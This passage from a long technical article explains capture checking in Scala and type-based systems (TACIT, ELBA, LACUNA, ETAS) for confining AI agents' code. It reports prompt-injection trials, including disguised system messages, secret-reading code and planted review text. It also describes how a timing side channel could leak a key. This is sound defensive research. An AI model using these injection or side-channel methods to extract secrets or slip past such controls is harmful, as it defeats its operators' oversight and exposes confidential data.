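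Ordinary types don't help much either, since they leave out effects. A function of type Invoice → Money may be a closure, meaning it keeps variables from the surrounding code, and one of these may refer to the mail object. To find out, a reviewer has to locate where the program created the function and then check every function it calls.

### Effect systems and why few languages have them

In 1988, John Lucassen and David Gifford described a type system that records effects as well as values. Their effects were reading, writing and allocating memory in a particular region, and they wanted a compiler to find parts of a program that could safely run in parallel. In such a system, a function type has an effect *φ* attached to its arrow. If *f* is a function with effect *φ* and *e* is its argument, then

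effect(*f*(*e*)) = effect(*f*) ∪ effect(*e*) ∪ *φ*,

where effect(*f*) and effect(*e*) are whatever happens while the program works out the function and the argument. A function's effects therefore include those of every function it calls.

This rule causes trouble for functions that take other functions as arguments. Consider `map`, which applies a function to every item of a list. Its effects depend on the function it receives, so its type needs an extra variable E to stand for them:

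```
def map[B](f: A => B): List[B]                   // ordinary type
def map[B, E](f: A -> B eff E): List[B] eff E    // type with effects
```

One such signature is manageable, but nearly every method in an object-oriented language would need one, because it can end up calling code that its caller supplied. Boruch-Gruszecki, Odersky and colleagues argue in *Capturing Types* (2023) that this problem is the main reason effect systems are not in general use, despite hundreds of papers on them. Java's checked exceptions are one of the few widely implemented effect systems, and programmers often criticise them as verbose and rigid.

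If code can write to a file only through a reference to it, then a list of the references the code holds is also a limit on its effects. Craig, Potanin and colleagues proved a version of this for a small capability-safe language in 2018. Their bound requires no effect annotations inside the code, but it is loose because it includes everything the capabilities permit. In 2020, Brachthäuser and colleagues used a similar idea in a language called Effekt, where functions receive capabilities for their effects as parameters. The original design did not let programs return functions or store them in data structures, because a function could then hold a capability for too long. Capturing types remove that restriction by recording which capabilities each function keeps.

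### Capture sets in Scala 3

Scala is a general-purpose language that runs on the same platform as Java. With its capture checker switched on, a type can have the form

*T*^{*c*₁, …, *cₙ*},

where *T* is an ordinary type and the part in braces is the capture set, which lists the capabilities that a value of this type may hold. For functions, programmers write the set after the arrow:

| Type | Capabilities the function may hold |
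|---|---|
| `Invoice -> Money` | none |
| `Invoice ->{log} Money` | `log` |
| `Invoice => Money` | any |

The double arrow `=>` is short for `->{any}`, where `any` stands for arbitrary capabilities (older publications write `cap`). `File^` is short for `File^{any}`, and the `^` makes the compiler track the file as a capability.

To find a closure's capture set, the compiler collects the variables that its body uses and removes its own parameters. In simplified form, the rules of Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues are:

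cv(*x*) = {*x*}

cv(*f x*) = {*f*, *x*}

cv(*x* ⇒ *t*) = cv(*t*) \ {*x*}

The compiler can then drop any variable whose own type has an empty capture set. In the following code, one function calls another:

```
def makeStep(log: File^) =
  val record = (inv: Invoice) => log.write(inv.text)
  val step   = (inv: Invoice) => record(inv)
  step
```

The body of `record` uses `log` and `inv`. Removing the parameter `inv` leaves {log}. The body of `step` uses `record` and `inv`, so removing `inv` leaves {record}. `step` doesn't refer to the log directly, but the type of `record` is `Invoice ->{log} Unit`, so whoever can call `record` can cause a write to the log. (`Unit` is the result type of a function that returns nothing useful.) When `makeStep` returns `step`, the name `record` goes out of scope, so the compiler replaces it with `log`, and the returned function has type `Invoice ->{log} Unit`.

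Programmers rarely have to write capture sets inside a function. According to *Formalizing Box Inference for Capture Calculus* (2023), Scala first checks the ordinary types and ignores the capture sets. A second pass works out what each closure captures, fills in sets that the programmer left out, and compares the results with the annotations.

The comparison follows a subtyping rule. Writing *A* <: *B* for "a value of type *A* can go wherever the program expects a *B*", the rule is

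*T*₁^*C*₁ <: *T*₂^*C*₂ if *T*₁ <: *T*₂ and *C*₁ <: *C*₂.

For capture sets, *C*₁ <: *C*₂ means that *C*₂ covers *C*₁, which holds if every capability in *C*₁ either is a member of *C*₂ or has a type whose own capture set is covered by *C*₂. A value that may hold less can be used where one that may hold more is expected, provided that the ordinary types match. In the example, {log} covers {record} because `record` gets its access from `log`, but {record} does not cover {log}. The set {any} covers everything, and the empty set covers only itself and sets that contain nothing tracked.

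This also solves the problem with `map` without changing its signature. Its parameter, `f: A => B`, already has a double arrow in ordinary Scala, so `map` accepts functions that hold any capabilities. `map` itself holds none, and the compiler counts the capabilities of `f` wherever a program calls `map` with it.

### What an empty capture set guarantees

A function with an empty capture set is pure in the sense that it holds no capabilities, but its caller may still pass it one. For example, a function of type `File^ -> Unit` is pure, and it can write to whatever file it receives. *Recovering Purity with Comonads and Capabilities* (Choudhury and Krishnaswami, 2019) discusses a similar function that takes a list of output channels and a piece of text. If the function holds no channels of its own, it can print only to the channels in the list, so it cannot print anything when the list is empty.

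If neither a function nor its argument holds a capability, the function can do nothing except compute a result. A function of type `Invoice -> Money` meets this condition as long as an invoice is plain data. Scala also treats mutable variables as capabilities, so a pure function cannot leave a message in a shared variable for another function to send. A pure function can still run forever or fail with an error such as division by zero, because neither requires a capability.

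### A supposedly pure function that writes to a file

Suppose that the firm has a function for adding up what it owes, and wants to be sure that the calculation has no other effects:

```
def total(invoices: List[Invoice], due: Invoice -> Money): Money =   // 1
  invoices.map(due).sum                                              // 2

def report(invoices: List[Invoice], log: File^): Money =             // 3
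  total(invoices, inv => { log.write(inv.text); inv.amount })        // 4, error
```

The function `due` finds the amount owed on one invoice. Its type on line 1 has a single arrow and no capture set, so `due` must be pure. Line 2 applies `due` to each invoice and adds up the results. Line 3 gives `report` a log file, which is fine because `report` may need one.

In line 4, `report` supplies a function that returns the right amount but first copies the invoice's text to the log. The body uses `log`, so the compiler gives the function the type `Invoice ->{log} Money`. Line 1 requires `Invoice -> Money`. The ordinary types match, so the compiler accepts the function only if {} covers {log}. The empty set does not cover {log}, because it does not contain `log` and does not cover {any}, the capture set in `log`'s type. The compiler therefore rejects line 4 before the program can run.

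Moving the write into a helper function would not get around this, because the helper's capture set would contain `log` and the compiler would track that capture through the helper. The author could delete the write, or change the single arrow in line 1 to a double one. Changing the arrow alters the signature of `total`, so a reviewer who relied on its purity can see the change.

### A file handle that outlives its scope

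The types can also limit how long code keeps a capability. This example comes from Scala's *Capture Checking Basics*:

```
def usingLogFile[T](op: FileOutputStream^ => T): T =        // 1
  val logFile = FileOutputStream("log")                     // 2
  val result = op(logFile)                                  // 3
  logFile.close()                                           // 4
  result                                                    // 5

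val later = usingLogFile { file => () => file.write(0) }    // 6, error
later()                                                     // 7
```

The function opens a log file, lets an operation `op` use it, closes it and returns the operation's result, which can have any type `T` (line 1). The operation in line 6 returns a new function that writes only when called. Line 7 calls that function after line 4 has closed the file. Without capture checking, the program compiles and crashes at line 7.

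With capture checking, the inner function `() => file.write(0)` has type `() ->{file} Unit`. For line 6 to be valid, `T` must be a type that fits this function. The caller of `usingLogFile` chooses `T` outside the operation, where `file` is not in scope, so the capture set of `T` cannot include `file`. The compiler also doesn't allow `any` in its place, so no type fits and the compiler rejects line 6.

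The check distinguishes programs that look almost identical. The compiler accepts an operation that goes through an ordinary list and writes each number to the file, because all the writing happens before line 4. It rejects the same operation on a lazy list, which calculates each item only when it is needed and so has to keep the file for later. It also rejects assigning the inner function to a variable outside the operation, because that variable's capture set cannot include `file` either.

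A harness could use the same pattern to lend an agent's program the invoice folder for one task. The forwarder described earlier also ends access when the task is over, but if the program kept a reference, the mistake would show up only when a call failed. The two methods work well together because the forwarder works even if no one has checked the code.

### Collections and kinds of capability

In Scala, a collection's capture set leaves out the capabilities that its elements capture. A list of functions that read from the console has the type `List[() ->{console} Int]`, and the list itself counts as pure. Code can count the functions without holding `console`, but when it takes one out of the list, the compiler adds `console` to the code's capture set. In the theory, the list keeps each function in a "box" that hides the function's capabilities until code opens the box.

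The 2023 version of the theory could not handle some common cases, such as a program that starts several downloads and collects the results in a stream, in order of completion. If the capture set of the downloads was {any}, the rules did not let the program open the boxes around the downloads. *What's in the Box* (Xu, Bračevac and colleagues, 2025) solved this by introducing a name for whatever capabilities a collection's items hold. The stream's type can then show that the stream holds no more capabilities than the downloads did.

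Capture sets were also limited because they could list particular capabilities but not kinds of capabilities. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (Pham, Bračevac and colleagues, 2026) describes an error in Scala's standard library that resulted from this. `Try` runs a function, catches any exception it throws, and stores the outcome. The library declared the stored outcome to be pure, which was wrong even though `Try` does not keep the function. When a program later asks for the result, `Try` throws any stored exception again, and throwing an exception requires a capability in this system.

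One solution arranges kinds of capability in a tree. A type can then keep only the capabilities in one branch, as in `body.only[Control]`, or exclude those in a branch, as in `any.except[ThreadLocal]`. The first form gives `Try` its correct type. Different branches never overlap, even if somebody adds new kinds later, so the compiler can check an exclusion without knowing every kind that exists.

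Pham and colleagues reproduced 59 patterns from existing software that depend on excluding effects. In one, from Google's cloud library, a function receives a database transaction but must not commit it or roll it back, because the library does that. Similarly, a payment library could let agent-written code add payments to a batch but not send the batch.

### What the proofs cover

Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues proved that a program which passes the checks never gets stuck on a type error, and that its types remain valid as it runs. They also proved that the capture set predicts what the program does. If *t* is a well-typed program, then

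{primitive capabilities used while *t* runs} ⊆ cv(*t*).

A primitive capability here is one that exists throughout the run, such as access to the file system. This theorem lets a reviewer rely on the signature without reading the body. *A Mechanized Theory of the Box Calculus* (2023) describes work on checking the proofs about this system by computer. For the 2025 version, Xu and colleagues checked the main proofs in Lean, a program that verifies mathematical proofs. They proved on paper that the notation programmers write translates correctly into the underlying theory. Pham and colleagues also checked their safety proofs in Lean.

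All these proofs concern small model languages. The 2023 model leaves out classes, objects, modules and mutable variables, although Scala's compiler has rules for all of them. Nobody has proved that the compiler implements the theory correctly, whereas the seL4 proofs do connect a specification to C code. Xu and colleagues report that earlier attempts in the compiler to name the contents of boxes had several soundness errors, so it could accept unsafe programs. These errors were part of the reason for developing a new theory. The theorems also assume that the types of primitive operations are correct. If a library author declares that a function is pure and the compiler does not check its body, every conclusion that relies on the declaration may be wrong.

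### Wyvern and Gradient: limiting what libraries can do

A modern application may use hundreds of third-party libraries, any of which could be malicious or become so in an update. The research language Wyvern addresses this by making each module a capability. A module that needs the network has to list it as a parameter, and the code that loads the module has to supply it. In 2017, Melicher, Shi and colleagues proved that the core of the language controls access in this way. A reviewer can work out what a module may use from its interface and the objects the program passes to it.

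Melicher and colleagues defined authority in a way that is closer to what Miller calls permission. In Wyvern, a module that holds only a logger does not have authority over the log file, even though it can cause writes to the file. An advantage of this definition is that the analysis treats a wrapper such as the firm's payer as a restriction. Scala's rules follow the chain from the logger to the file, which gives a safer bound but can make a weak capability look like a strong one.

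Boruch-Gruszecki, Ghosn and colleagues (2024), in *Gradient*, argue that languages like Wyvern and E have seen little industrial use because they require the whole program to give up ambient authority, including libraries that developers adopted to save themselves work. Gradient is a proof-of-concept extension of Scala in which a program can convert its libraries one at a time, in any order. It offers different protection at each stage:

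- A library without capture sets can run only inside an `enclosed` block, which lists the resources it may use. A run-time mechanism stops the program if the library exceeds the list.
- A library with capture sets can still reach the file system directly, but the program can call it inside a `restricted` block, and the compiler checks that it uses only the listed resources.
- A fully converted library receives all its capabilities as parameters, so the program can also hand it weakened ones, such as a file system object that opens only files in `/var/log`.

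The running example is Log4j, a Java logging library. In 2021, attackers found that they could run code on a server by getting it to log a specially written line of text. If Log4j had been fully converted to typed capabilities, it would have had to request the file system, the network and the ability to run new code. If an update had added the request to run new code, programs using Log4j would have stopped compiling until somebody approved the change.

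Gradient also prevents libraries from keeping capabilities they only need briefly. A library that extracts text from scanned documents might use the network once to update its models. If it could store that network capability, it could later send out the private documents it scanned. Gradient rejects code that retrieves a capability from storage unless it comes from capabilities the code already has.

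Boruch-Gruszecki, Ghosn and colleagues tested whether conversion is practical by adding capture sets to Scala's standard XML library, and concluded that it is. Their test covers only the middle stage, because the library kept its existing structure and did not have to take its capabilities as parameters, which is the more demanding step. One library is also a small sample, and an XML library has less reason to use the network or run new code than many of the libraries people worry about.

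### Pony's reference capabilities

In Pony, a concurrent programming language, "capability" has two meanings. Pony has ordinary object capabilities, so a program needs a suitable object to open a file. Every reference also has a "reference capability", which controls whether code may use it to read or change the object and what other code may hold references to that object. For example, `iso` marks the only reference through which any code can read or change an object, and `val` marks an object that no code can change, so any number of program parts can share it.

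These markings prevent data races, in which one part of a program changes something while another part is using it. They do not limit which outside resources a program can reach. An `iso` reference to the firm's bank connection would ensure that only one part of the program used it at a time, but that part could still pay anyone. *Linearly Qualified Types* (Spiwack, Kiss and colleagues, 2022) uses "capability" differently, to mean permission to read or write an array, and the compiler tracks that permission separately from the array.

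### Four objections to capturing types

A capture set only limits what a function may do. If a function writes to the log in a branch that never runs, `log` is still in its set. More seriously, the compiler can lose sight of a wrapper. Suppose a function creates the firm's payer from a bank connection and returns a closure that uses it:

```
def makePayment(bank: Bank^, register: Register): Invoice ->{bank} Unit =
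  val payer: Payer^{bank} = makePayer(bank, register)
  inv => payer.pay(inv.supplier, inv.amount)
```

The closure holds only the payer, which pays nobody outside the register. But `payer` is a local name, so the result's type has to mention `bank` instead, and a reviewer who reads only the type would have to assume that the function can pay anyone. Such errors are safe because they overstate what the code can do. Creating the payer first and passing it in as a parameter avoids the problem, because the caller can then see its name. The set also doesn't record the size or number of payments. Limiting those requires numbers in the types or in the objects.

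Evidence from Scala's own libraries weakens another common objection, that programmers will not put up with the annotations. When Xu and colleagues converted the collections library, about 30,000 lines, they changed less than 5% of the code and left almost 90% of function signatures unchanged. Pham and colleagues needed 165 uses of `.only` and `.except` in the whole standard library and noticed no slowdown in compilation. But the people who converted these libraries also designed the system, and most collection operations are simple to annotate because they just call the function they receive. Business software that opens files and connections throughout may need more changes.

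Scala reduces this work by passing capabilities to functions automatically, so programmers don't have to write them in each call. It also permits global capabilities, which the traditional object-capability model forbids because any code could use them. According to Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview*, they are acceptable because a function that uses one, such as `Console.out`, has it in its capture set, and the compiler rejects that function wherever the program requires a pure one. Global capabilities save programmers from restructuring old programs, but without the compiler's check they would be ambient authority.

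Error messages can also be hard to understand. SoftwareMill's *Understanding capture checking in Scala* describes the compiler's message for a leaked file as "quite complex and opaque". An AI agent might handle such messages better than a person who rarely sees them, but a reviewer still has to understand the signatures.

Capture checking is also still experimental. One page of Scala's documentation calls it "highly experimental and unstable", but the *Tracked Capabilities Overview*, which uses the newer notation, calls it "quite mature" and says the developers expect to stabilise it soon. Version 3.9, which the project recommends for cautious production users, makes one new language feature permanent (Mazur, *Scala 3.9 LTS released!*), but that feature is unrelated to capture checking. A firm that adopts capture checking now has to accept that its rules may change.

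The remaining objection is that the compiler does not fully check some code. Scala has casts, reflection and annotations that turn off particular checks, and any of them can stop the compiler from tracking a capability. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a "safe mode" that forbids these features in agent-written programs. But libraries may need them. For instance, a function might store earlier results to avoid repeating a calculation, which changes a variable but has no effect that its callers can observe. The library's author can mark such code `@assumeSafe`, and is then responsible for its safety.

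Pham and colleagues report that the compiler now checks 45,146 of the standard library's 54,992 lines for captures, about 82%, compared with about 67% before their work. That leaves nearly 10,000 unchecked lines, and someone has to decide which of the functions in them agents may call in safe mode. Joe-E's developers faced the same task when they tamed Java's library, and E's developers made mistakes when they did it. Choudhury and Krishnaswami suggest treating every library function as impure until somebody has audited it. Ordinary code could still use the whole library, and only code that has to be pure would be limited to the audited part. Failing to audit a pure function would then cause an inconvenient compiler error, whereas wrongly marking a function as safe could let an agent's program write to a file from code that the compiler accepts as pure.

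## AI agents that write capability-typed programs

Capture checking works on programs, so it can't be applied to an agent that makes one tool call at a time. A call such as "pay supplier 17 €940" contains no functions for a compiler to check. But many agents now write programs that combine several tools with loops and conditions, partly because this takes less text than a separate call for each step. If the firm's agent submits its whole invoice program, the harness can compile it before the first payment. If the last line needs a capability the program lacks, the compiler rejects the program and no money moves, whereas the CapScope harness of Bouras and colleagues would stop only the last call.

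This advantage applies to one program at a time. An agent may run a program, read its results and write another, and rejecting the second does not undo what the first one did.

### TACIT

Odersky and colleagues built TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), first released in March 2026, to put capture checking between an agent and its tools. TACIT is a Model Context Protocol server, so existing agents can connect to it without modification. The agent sends Scala code as the argument of a tool call. If the code compiles, TACIT runs it and returns the output. If it doesn't, the agent gets the compiler's error messages and can try again.

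The agent's code can affect the outside world only through TACIT's library. A call to `requestFileSystem("/firm/invoices")` gives the code a capability for that folder until the end of a block, and the compiler rejects code that would keep it longer. The types don't record which folder it is, so the library checks each path at run time and refuses any outside the folder. Similar functions give access to listed websites and commands. Since the agent's code names the folder, the firm would also have to limit which folders the library can give access to.

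Odersky and colleagues argue that a language for agents has to meet three requirements:

- Capability safety: code cannot forge a capability, or use one without the compiler noticing.
- Capability completeness: every effect that matters for safety requires a capability, except for a few that the harness contains at run time.
- Local purity: the type system can state that a particular piece of code uses only certain capabilities, or none at all.

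Older capability languages such as E and Joe-E were designed to meet the first two, but they rely on run-time mechanisms, so their types can't express that a function holds no capabilities. Haskell's types can express this, but Haskell has no built-in object capabilities. Odersky and colleagues chose Scala because they consider it the only production-ready language whose types track capabilities.

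### What safe mode forbids

Casts and similar features keep Scala as a whole from meeting the first requirement, so TACIT compiles agents' code in safe mode, which Scala's *Safe Mode* describes as a subset of the language in which code cannot "forget" tracked capabilities. It has six rules:

1. No unchecked casts or pattern matches.
2. Nothing from the `caps.unsafe` module.
3. No `@unchecked` annotations, which switch off compiler checks.
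4. No reflection at run time.
5. Capture checking must be on, including for changes to variables, and the compiler must track which values may be null.
6. Code may use global objects and functions only if their own code is safe.

The sixth rule excludes Scala's ordinary print functions, since any code could use them to send out data. TACIT's library provides replacements that require a capability.

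Exceptions are harder to exclude, because a program can always run out of memory or divide by zero. They could carry secret text out of a function, so TACIT catches them and turns them into ordinary values, which it can protect like other data. The compiler also prevents exceptions from containing capabilities. Joe-E solved this problem by making exceptions immutable.

Safe mode is even newer than capture checking. When the software company VirtusLab described it in *Safe Scala*, it was available only in nightly builds of the compiler. VirtusLab recommends combining it with a sandbox.

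### Working on text the agent cannot read

TACIT's main use of local purity is to let an agent process documents without seeing them. Suppose that the firm doesn't want the company hosting the agent's model to read its invoices. It marks the invoice folder as classified, and the library then returns each file's text inside a container of type `Classified[String]`. The agent's code can work on the text only through methods such as `map`:

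```
requestFileSystem("/firm") {
  val invoice = readClassified("/firm/invoices/17.txt")   // 1
  val length  = invoice.map(text => text.length)          // 2
  val log     = access("/firm/log.txt")                   // 3
  invoice.map(text => log.write(text))                    // 4, error
}
```

`map` applies a function to the hidden text and puts the result in a new container. It accepts only functions with an empty capture set. The function in line 2 holds no capabilities, so the compiler accepts it, and `length` has the type `Classified[Int]`. The function in line 4 has the type `String ->{log} Unit`, so the compiler rejects the program. It would also reject a function that printed the text, sent it over the network or called `requestFileSystem`, because each of these requires a capability.

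Summarising a contract, unlike counting characters, requires a language model, so TACIT can connect to a second model that the user trusts, perhaps one on the firm's own computer. The library's `chat` function takes a request and a classified text, and returns the second model's answer in a container. A hidden line in a contract might distort the summary, but the second model has no tools and the first model never reads the contract. The types cannot guarantee that the second model's service deletes the text afterwards, so its operator must ensure this.

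The user still needs to see the summary, so when the code prints a classified value, TACIT sends the real text to the user's terminal and only `Classified(****)` to the agent. The container also persists between programs, so if the user next asks how long the summary is, the agent can write code that computes and prints the length, again without seeing it.

This arrangement makes some mistakes hard for the agent to notice. If a function inside `map` fails, TACIT hides the error message in case it contains secret text. In one set of tests, Odersky and colleagues had to warn the model that its code might appear to succeed while the user saw nothing.

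### Results from 131 trials per condition

Odersky and colleagues tested the container on a small software project with a folder of passwords, a database and confidential documents. They gave an agent 12 legitimate tasks, such as listing a program's functions or summarising a confidential incident report, and combined each with 10 injections. Some injections were disguised as system messages, and others contained finished Scala code for reading the secrets. In 11 further trials, the user was the attacker and either asked for the secrets directly or posed as someone entitled to them.

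All 131 trials ran with the container and again with secrets as plain text, using two models from early 2026. A leak meant a secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Container | Leaks in 120 injected tasks | Leaks in 11 malicious requests | Trials without a leak | Injected tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | on | 0 | 0 | 100% | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | off | 0 | 2 | 98.5% | 83.3% |
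| MiniMax M2.5 | on | 0 | 0 | 100% | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | off | 3 | 8 | 91.6% | 88.3% |

Sonnet resisted every injection without help, so for that model the container made a difference only to the 11 malicious requests. Eleven trials without a leak would be compatible with a true leak rate of up to 24% at 95% confidence. The rule that `map` accepts only pure functions is a stronger reason to expect no leaks. The trials mainly show that the software applies this rule to ordinary attempts at theft. An attacker who knew of a compiler bug might do better, and the ten injections did not come from a search for one.

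Sonnet completed 99.2% of tasks with the container and 83.3% without it, but this is not clear evidence that the container makes agents more capable. Odersky and colleagues suspect that their time and turn limits affected the result. Without the container, Sonnet often exceeded these limits, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

### The AgentDojo port

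AgentDojo is a public benchmark that gives agents tasks in simulated banking, office, Slack and travel software, and plants instructions in the data their tools return. Odersky and colleagues ran it through TACIT with Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high. The benchmark counted one of about 1,900 attacks as successful. In that attack, the user had asked the agent to book a hotel, and an attacker had put a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, including the attacker's recommendation. The benchmark counted this as a success because the other hotel's name appeared in the output. The policy allowed the agent to show public reviews to the user, so the attack did not break any rule that TACIT enforced.

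In some areas, TACIT completed fewer tasks than CaMeL, an earlier system that tracks data while a program runs. With o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks and 48% of the Slack tasks, compared with 81% and 69% for CaMeL. Odersky and colleagues call the overall range comparable, which fits the Gemini results better than the o4-mini-high results. With Gemini, TACIT's scores in three areas ranged from 9 percentage points below CaMeL's to 4 above, and it completed 64% of the travel tasks, compared with 1% for CaMeL.

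It is also unclear how far the port tested the pure-function rule. The banking tools return files in a container, but some tasks involve acting on a file's contents. The port's `sendMoney` function lists no required capability, and the model's instructions explain that side effects inside `map` happen immediately and that it should place "commits" accordingly. This suggests that agents could make payments from inside `map`. If so, the low attack rate in the banking tasks is partly due to the models' own resistance to attacks.

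### Can models write this kind of code?

Models might have struggled with capture sets, because little of the text they learn from contains them. Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT with ordinary tool calls on two benchmarks. τ²-bench simulates customer service conversations, such as a request to change a flight. SWE-bench Lite consists of 300 real software problems from GitHub.

| Model | Interface | τ²-bench, airline | τ²-bench, retail | SWE-bench Lite |
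|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | tool calls | 43.8% | 53.3% | not tested |
| gpt-oss-120b | TACIT | 45.2% | 57.0% | not tested |
| MiniMax M2.5 | tool calls | 58.4% | 75.1% | 43.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | TACIT | 61.0% | 77.5% | 41.7% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | tool calls | 57.8% | 74.6% | not tested |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | TACIT | 58.6% | 75.5% | not tested |

On τ²-bench, between 0.3% and 7.9% of the programs needed a retry, usually only one. Common errors included forgetting that a value might be null and mistyping dollar signs in text. Compiling took less than a second, which is short compared with the time a model takes to write the code.

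The τ²-bench figures reflect the effect of typed Scala in general more than that of capabilities. Published signatures such as `cancelReservation(reservationId: String): Reservation` include no capabilities, and Odersky and colleagues attribute the improvement to clearer data types and useful error messages. SWE-bench Lite is a better test of capabilities because the agent had to request them for files and commands. TACIT solved five fewer of the 300 problems, a small difference, but only one model was tested.

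The setup also requires human work. TACIT's reusable part is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each τ²-bench domain needed a few hundred more to describe its tools. A model could write much of the domain-specific code from existing tool descriptions, but somebody has to review it before the agent starts.

### How far the guarantee goes

Odersky and colleagues say TACIT's guarantee does not depend on the agent's model, which they treat as a possible attacker. The guarantee is meant to hold even if an injection takes complete control of that model. It does depend on the Scala compiler, TACIT's library, the software that runs the compiled code, and the second model, and it covers only what somebody has marked as classified. Computers have checked proofs about the theory behind capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that a further argument is needed to show that safe mode provides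 the promised protection.

The types do not restrict what external commands can do. The Scala compiler does not check Python scripts, so if the firm lets the agent run Python, a script can read and send whatever the operating system allows. Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific, safe commands and adding a sandbox where security is critical.

Timing can also reveal secrets. A pure function could do a long calculation if the first bit of a secret key is 1 and finish at once if it is 0. The agent could then learn the bit from how long the program took, and 128 such programs could reveal a 128-bit key. TACIT isn't designed to prevent this.

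For the invoice agent, the more immediate problem is that a program can pass every check and still do the wrong thing. If the firm keeps its invoices classified, a pure function can extract the amount due but cannot pay it. To pay its bills, the firm would have to provide a payment function that accepts classified amounts, or allow payments inside `map`. In either case, a well-typed program could pay a false demand for €9,400.

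### Testing what happens after an injection succeeds

As models get better at resisting injection, ordinary attacks reveal less about how well the protection around the models works. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova ran into this problem in *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) with ELBA, a system similar to TACIT but written in Haskell. In ELBA, the type of answer a program expects limits what the agent's code may do. For example, if the program expects a whole number, the compiler rejects code that deletes files before returning one. The surrounding application is also in Haskell, so the same rules apply to it.

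Zhou and colleagues used the Slack tasks from AgentDojo with Claude Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, Sonnet 5 and GPT 5.4. All four models resisted all 105 attacks even without ELBA's policies. The researchers then changed the software so that a model which read a planted instruction received it as its entire task. With the policies off, 16% to 42% of these attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With them on, none of the 735 attacks on each model did. (The benchmark wrongly scored 29 runs as successes, and the researchers checked each of them by hand.)

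This is better evidence than TACIT's trials that protection can hold even when the model is compromised. However, the share of tasks completed under attack fell considerably, from 67–76% to 40–48%, because the policies restrict what a program may do after it reads untrusted data, which also blocks some legitimate actions. An existing Haskell library enforces the policies while the program runs, so the result supports the policies more than it supports checking types before the program runs.

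### LACUNA: filling gaps in a running program

TACIT's agent writes separate programs and sends them to a server. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, a paper from the same research group in May, instead put the model inside a program that people have written. The programmer leaves a gap where the model should supply code:

```
val due: List[Payment] = agent("list the payments due this month")
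```

When the program reaches this line, LACUNA sends the model the request, the surrounding code, the variables it can use and the type of result the program needs. The model writes code for the gap, and the compiler checks it as if a programmer had written it. Here the code must produce a list of payments. If no payment object is in scope at that point, the code can list payments but not make them. The programmer can grant different capabilities at each step by choosing where to put the gap.

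The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one example, the model's code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program expects a number. LACUNA rejects all of the code, so the balance doesn't change. An ordinary Python program would subtract the money before it reached the error.

However, the model's code may itself contain gaps, which LACUNA fills only when execution reaches them. The code could pay 30 suppliers and then reach a gap that the model fails to fill. Rejecting the code for that gap would not reverse the payments, so the firm would still have the problem that checking whole programs was supposed to solve.

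LACUNA also makes the classified container more flexible. In TACIT, the agent has to write the function for `map` without knowing what the document contains, but in LACUNA that function can include a gap that a trusted local model fills with suitable code after reading the document. The compiler still requires this code to be pure, so an instruction hidden in the document cannot make it send the text anywhere.

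Zhao and colleagues first checked the compiler on about 400 examples of valid and invalid code, and it handled all of them correctly. They then ran each of the 392 tasks in four areas of τ²-bench once. DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% of the tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls, though Zhao and colleagues call LACUNA's result "on par". In the retail tasks, the compiler rejected 22.4% of the model's code. For the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the rejection rate ranged from 3.2% in retail to 89% in telecom.

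TACIT and LACUNA both use typed Scala, but on the same benchmark TACIT's agents did slightly better than ordinary tool calls and LACUNA's did worse. The studies used different models and settings, so it's hard to isolate the cause. Zhao and colleagues chose low-cost models and turned off their reasoning for this test, so stronger models may do better. On BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 difficult research questions, the compiler rejected only 8.6% of DeepSeek's code. Zhao and colleagues attribute the higher rejection rate on the first benchmark to its conversations, where code has to combine tool results, earlier turns and the service's policies, but the model also had its reasoning turned on for the research questions. It answered 27.1% of them correctly, but the study doesn't compare this result with ordinary tool calls.

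Eight of about 1,900 AgentDojo attacks against LACUNA succeeded, seven of them with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues point out that the protection depends on how narrowly the programmer restricts access.

### Bastion and ETAS: proving more about a program

TACIT relies on its library to enforce limits such as which folder a capability covers. In *Modularizing Reasoning about AI Capabilities via Abstract Dijkstra Monads*, Omar, Ferris and Madhavapeddy (2024) proposed Bastion, a system that would prove that such limits hold. It would use F\*, a language whose types can state detailed properties of a program and whose compiler checks proofs of them.

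In Bastion, a capability is a module with a public list of commands and a hidden implementation. One example has commands for reading and writing files, with the permitted folders as parameters. The agent can only write programs that combine these commands. People would prove that the implementation never touches other folders, with help from AI systems that prove theorems.

Bastion would also let a second AI system narrow each grant to fit the task. If *A* is the access that the organisation's rules give an agent and *R* is what the second system wants to remove, the agent gets

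*A* \ *R* ⊆ *A*.

The second system's proposals can only reduce the agent's access. A faulty proposal might stop the agent from doing its job, but could not give it more access than the rules allow. Omar and colleagues presented this as a plan for a recently started project, in a proposal for a conference talk. They reported no experiments, and the proofs about the system were still to come.

Capture sets also don't record the order of a program's actions. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) presents a separate language for agents that does track this order. A programmer can require the program to request approval before any payment, and the compiler checks every route through the program. Where the compiler can't be sure, it adds a run-time check. ETAS counts a payment request even in a trial run that moves no money, so a test can expose a missing approval. In tests on small programs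 and coding tasks written in the language, ETAS enforced these rules without a mismatch.

The rule only requires a request for approval before the first payment, so one request is enough for any number of later payments. The program also has to check the answer separately, because code that asked the bookkeeper, was refused and paid anyway would still satisfy the rule.

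## When permitted calls add up to a forbidden result

An agent can stay within its permissions and still cause a result its owner forbids. *ChainCaps* (Jiang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that prepares a summary for executives. It reads a spreadsheet of salaries, fetches industry figures from the web, summarises the two together and emails the result to a distribution list. The agent has permission for each of these four calls, but together they send out salary data that the firm meant for internal use only.

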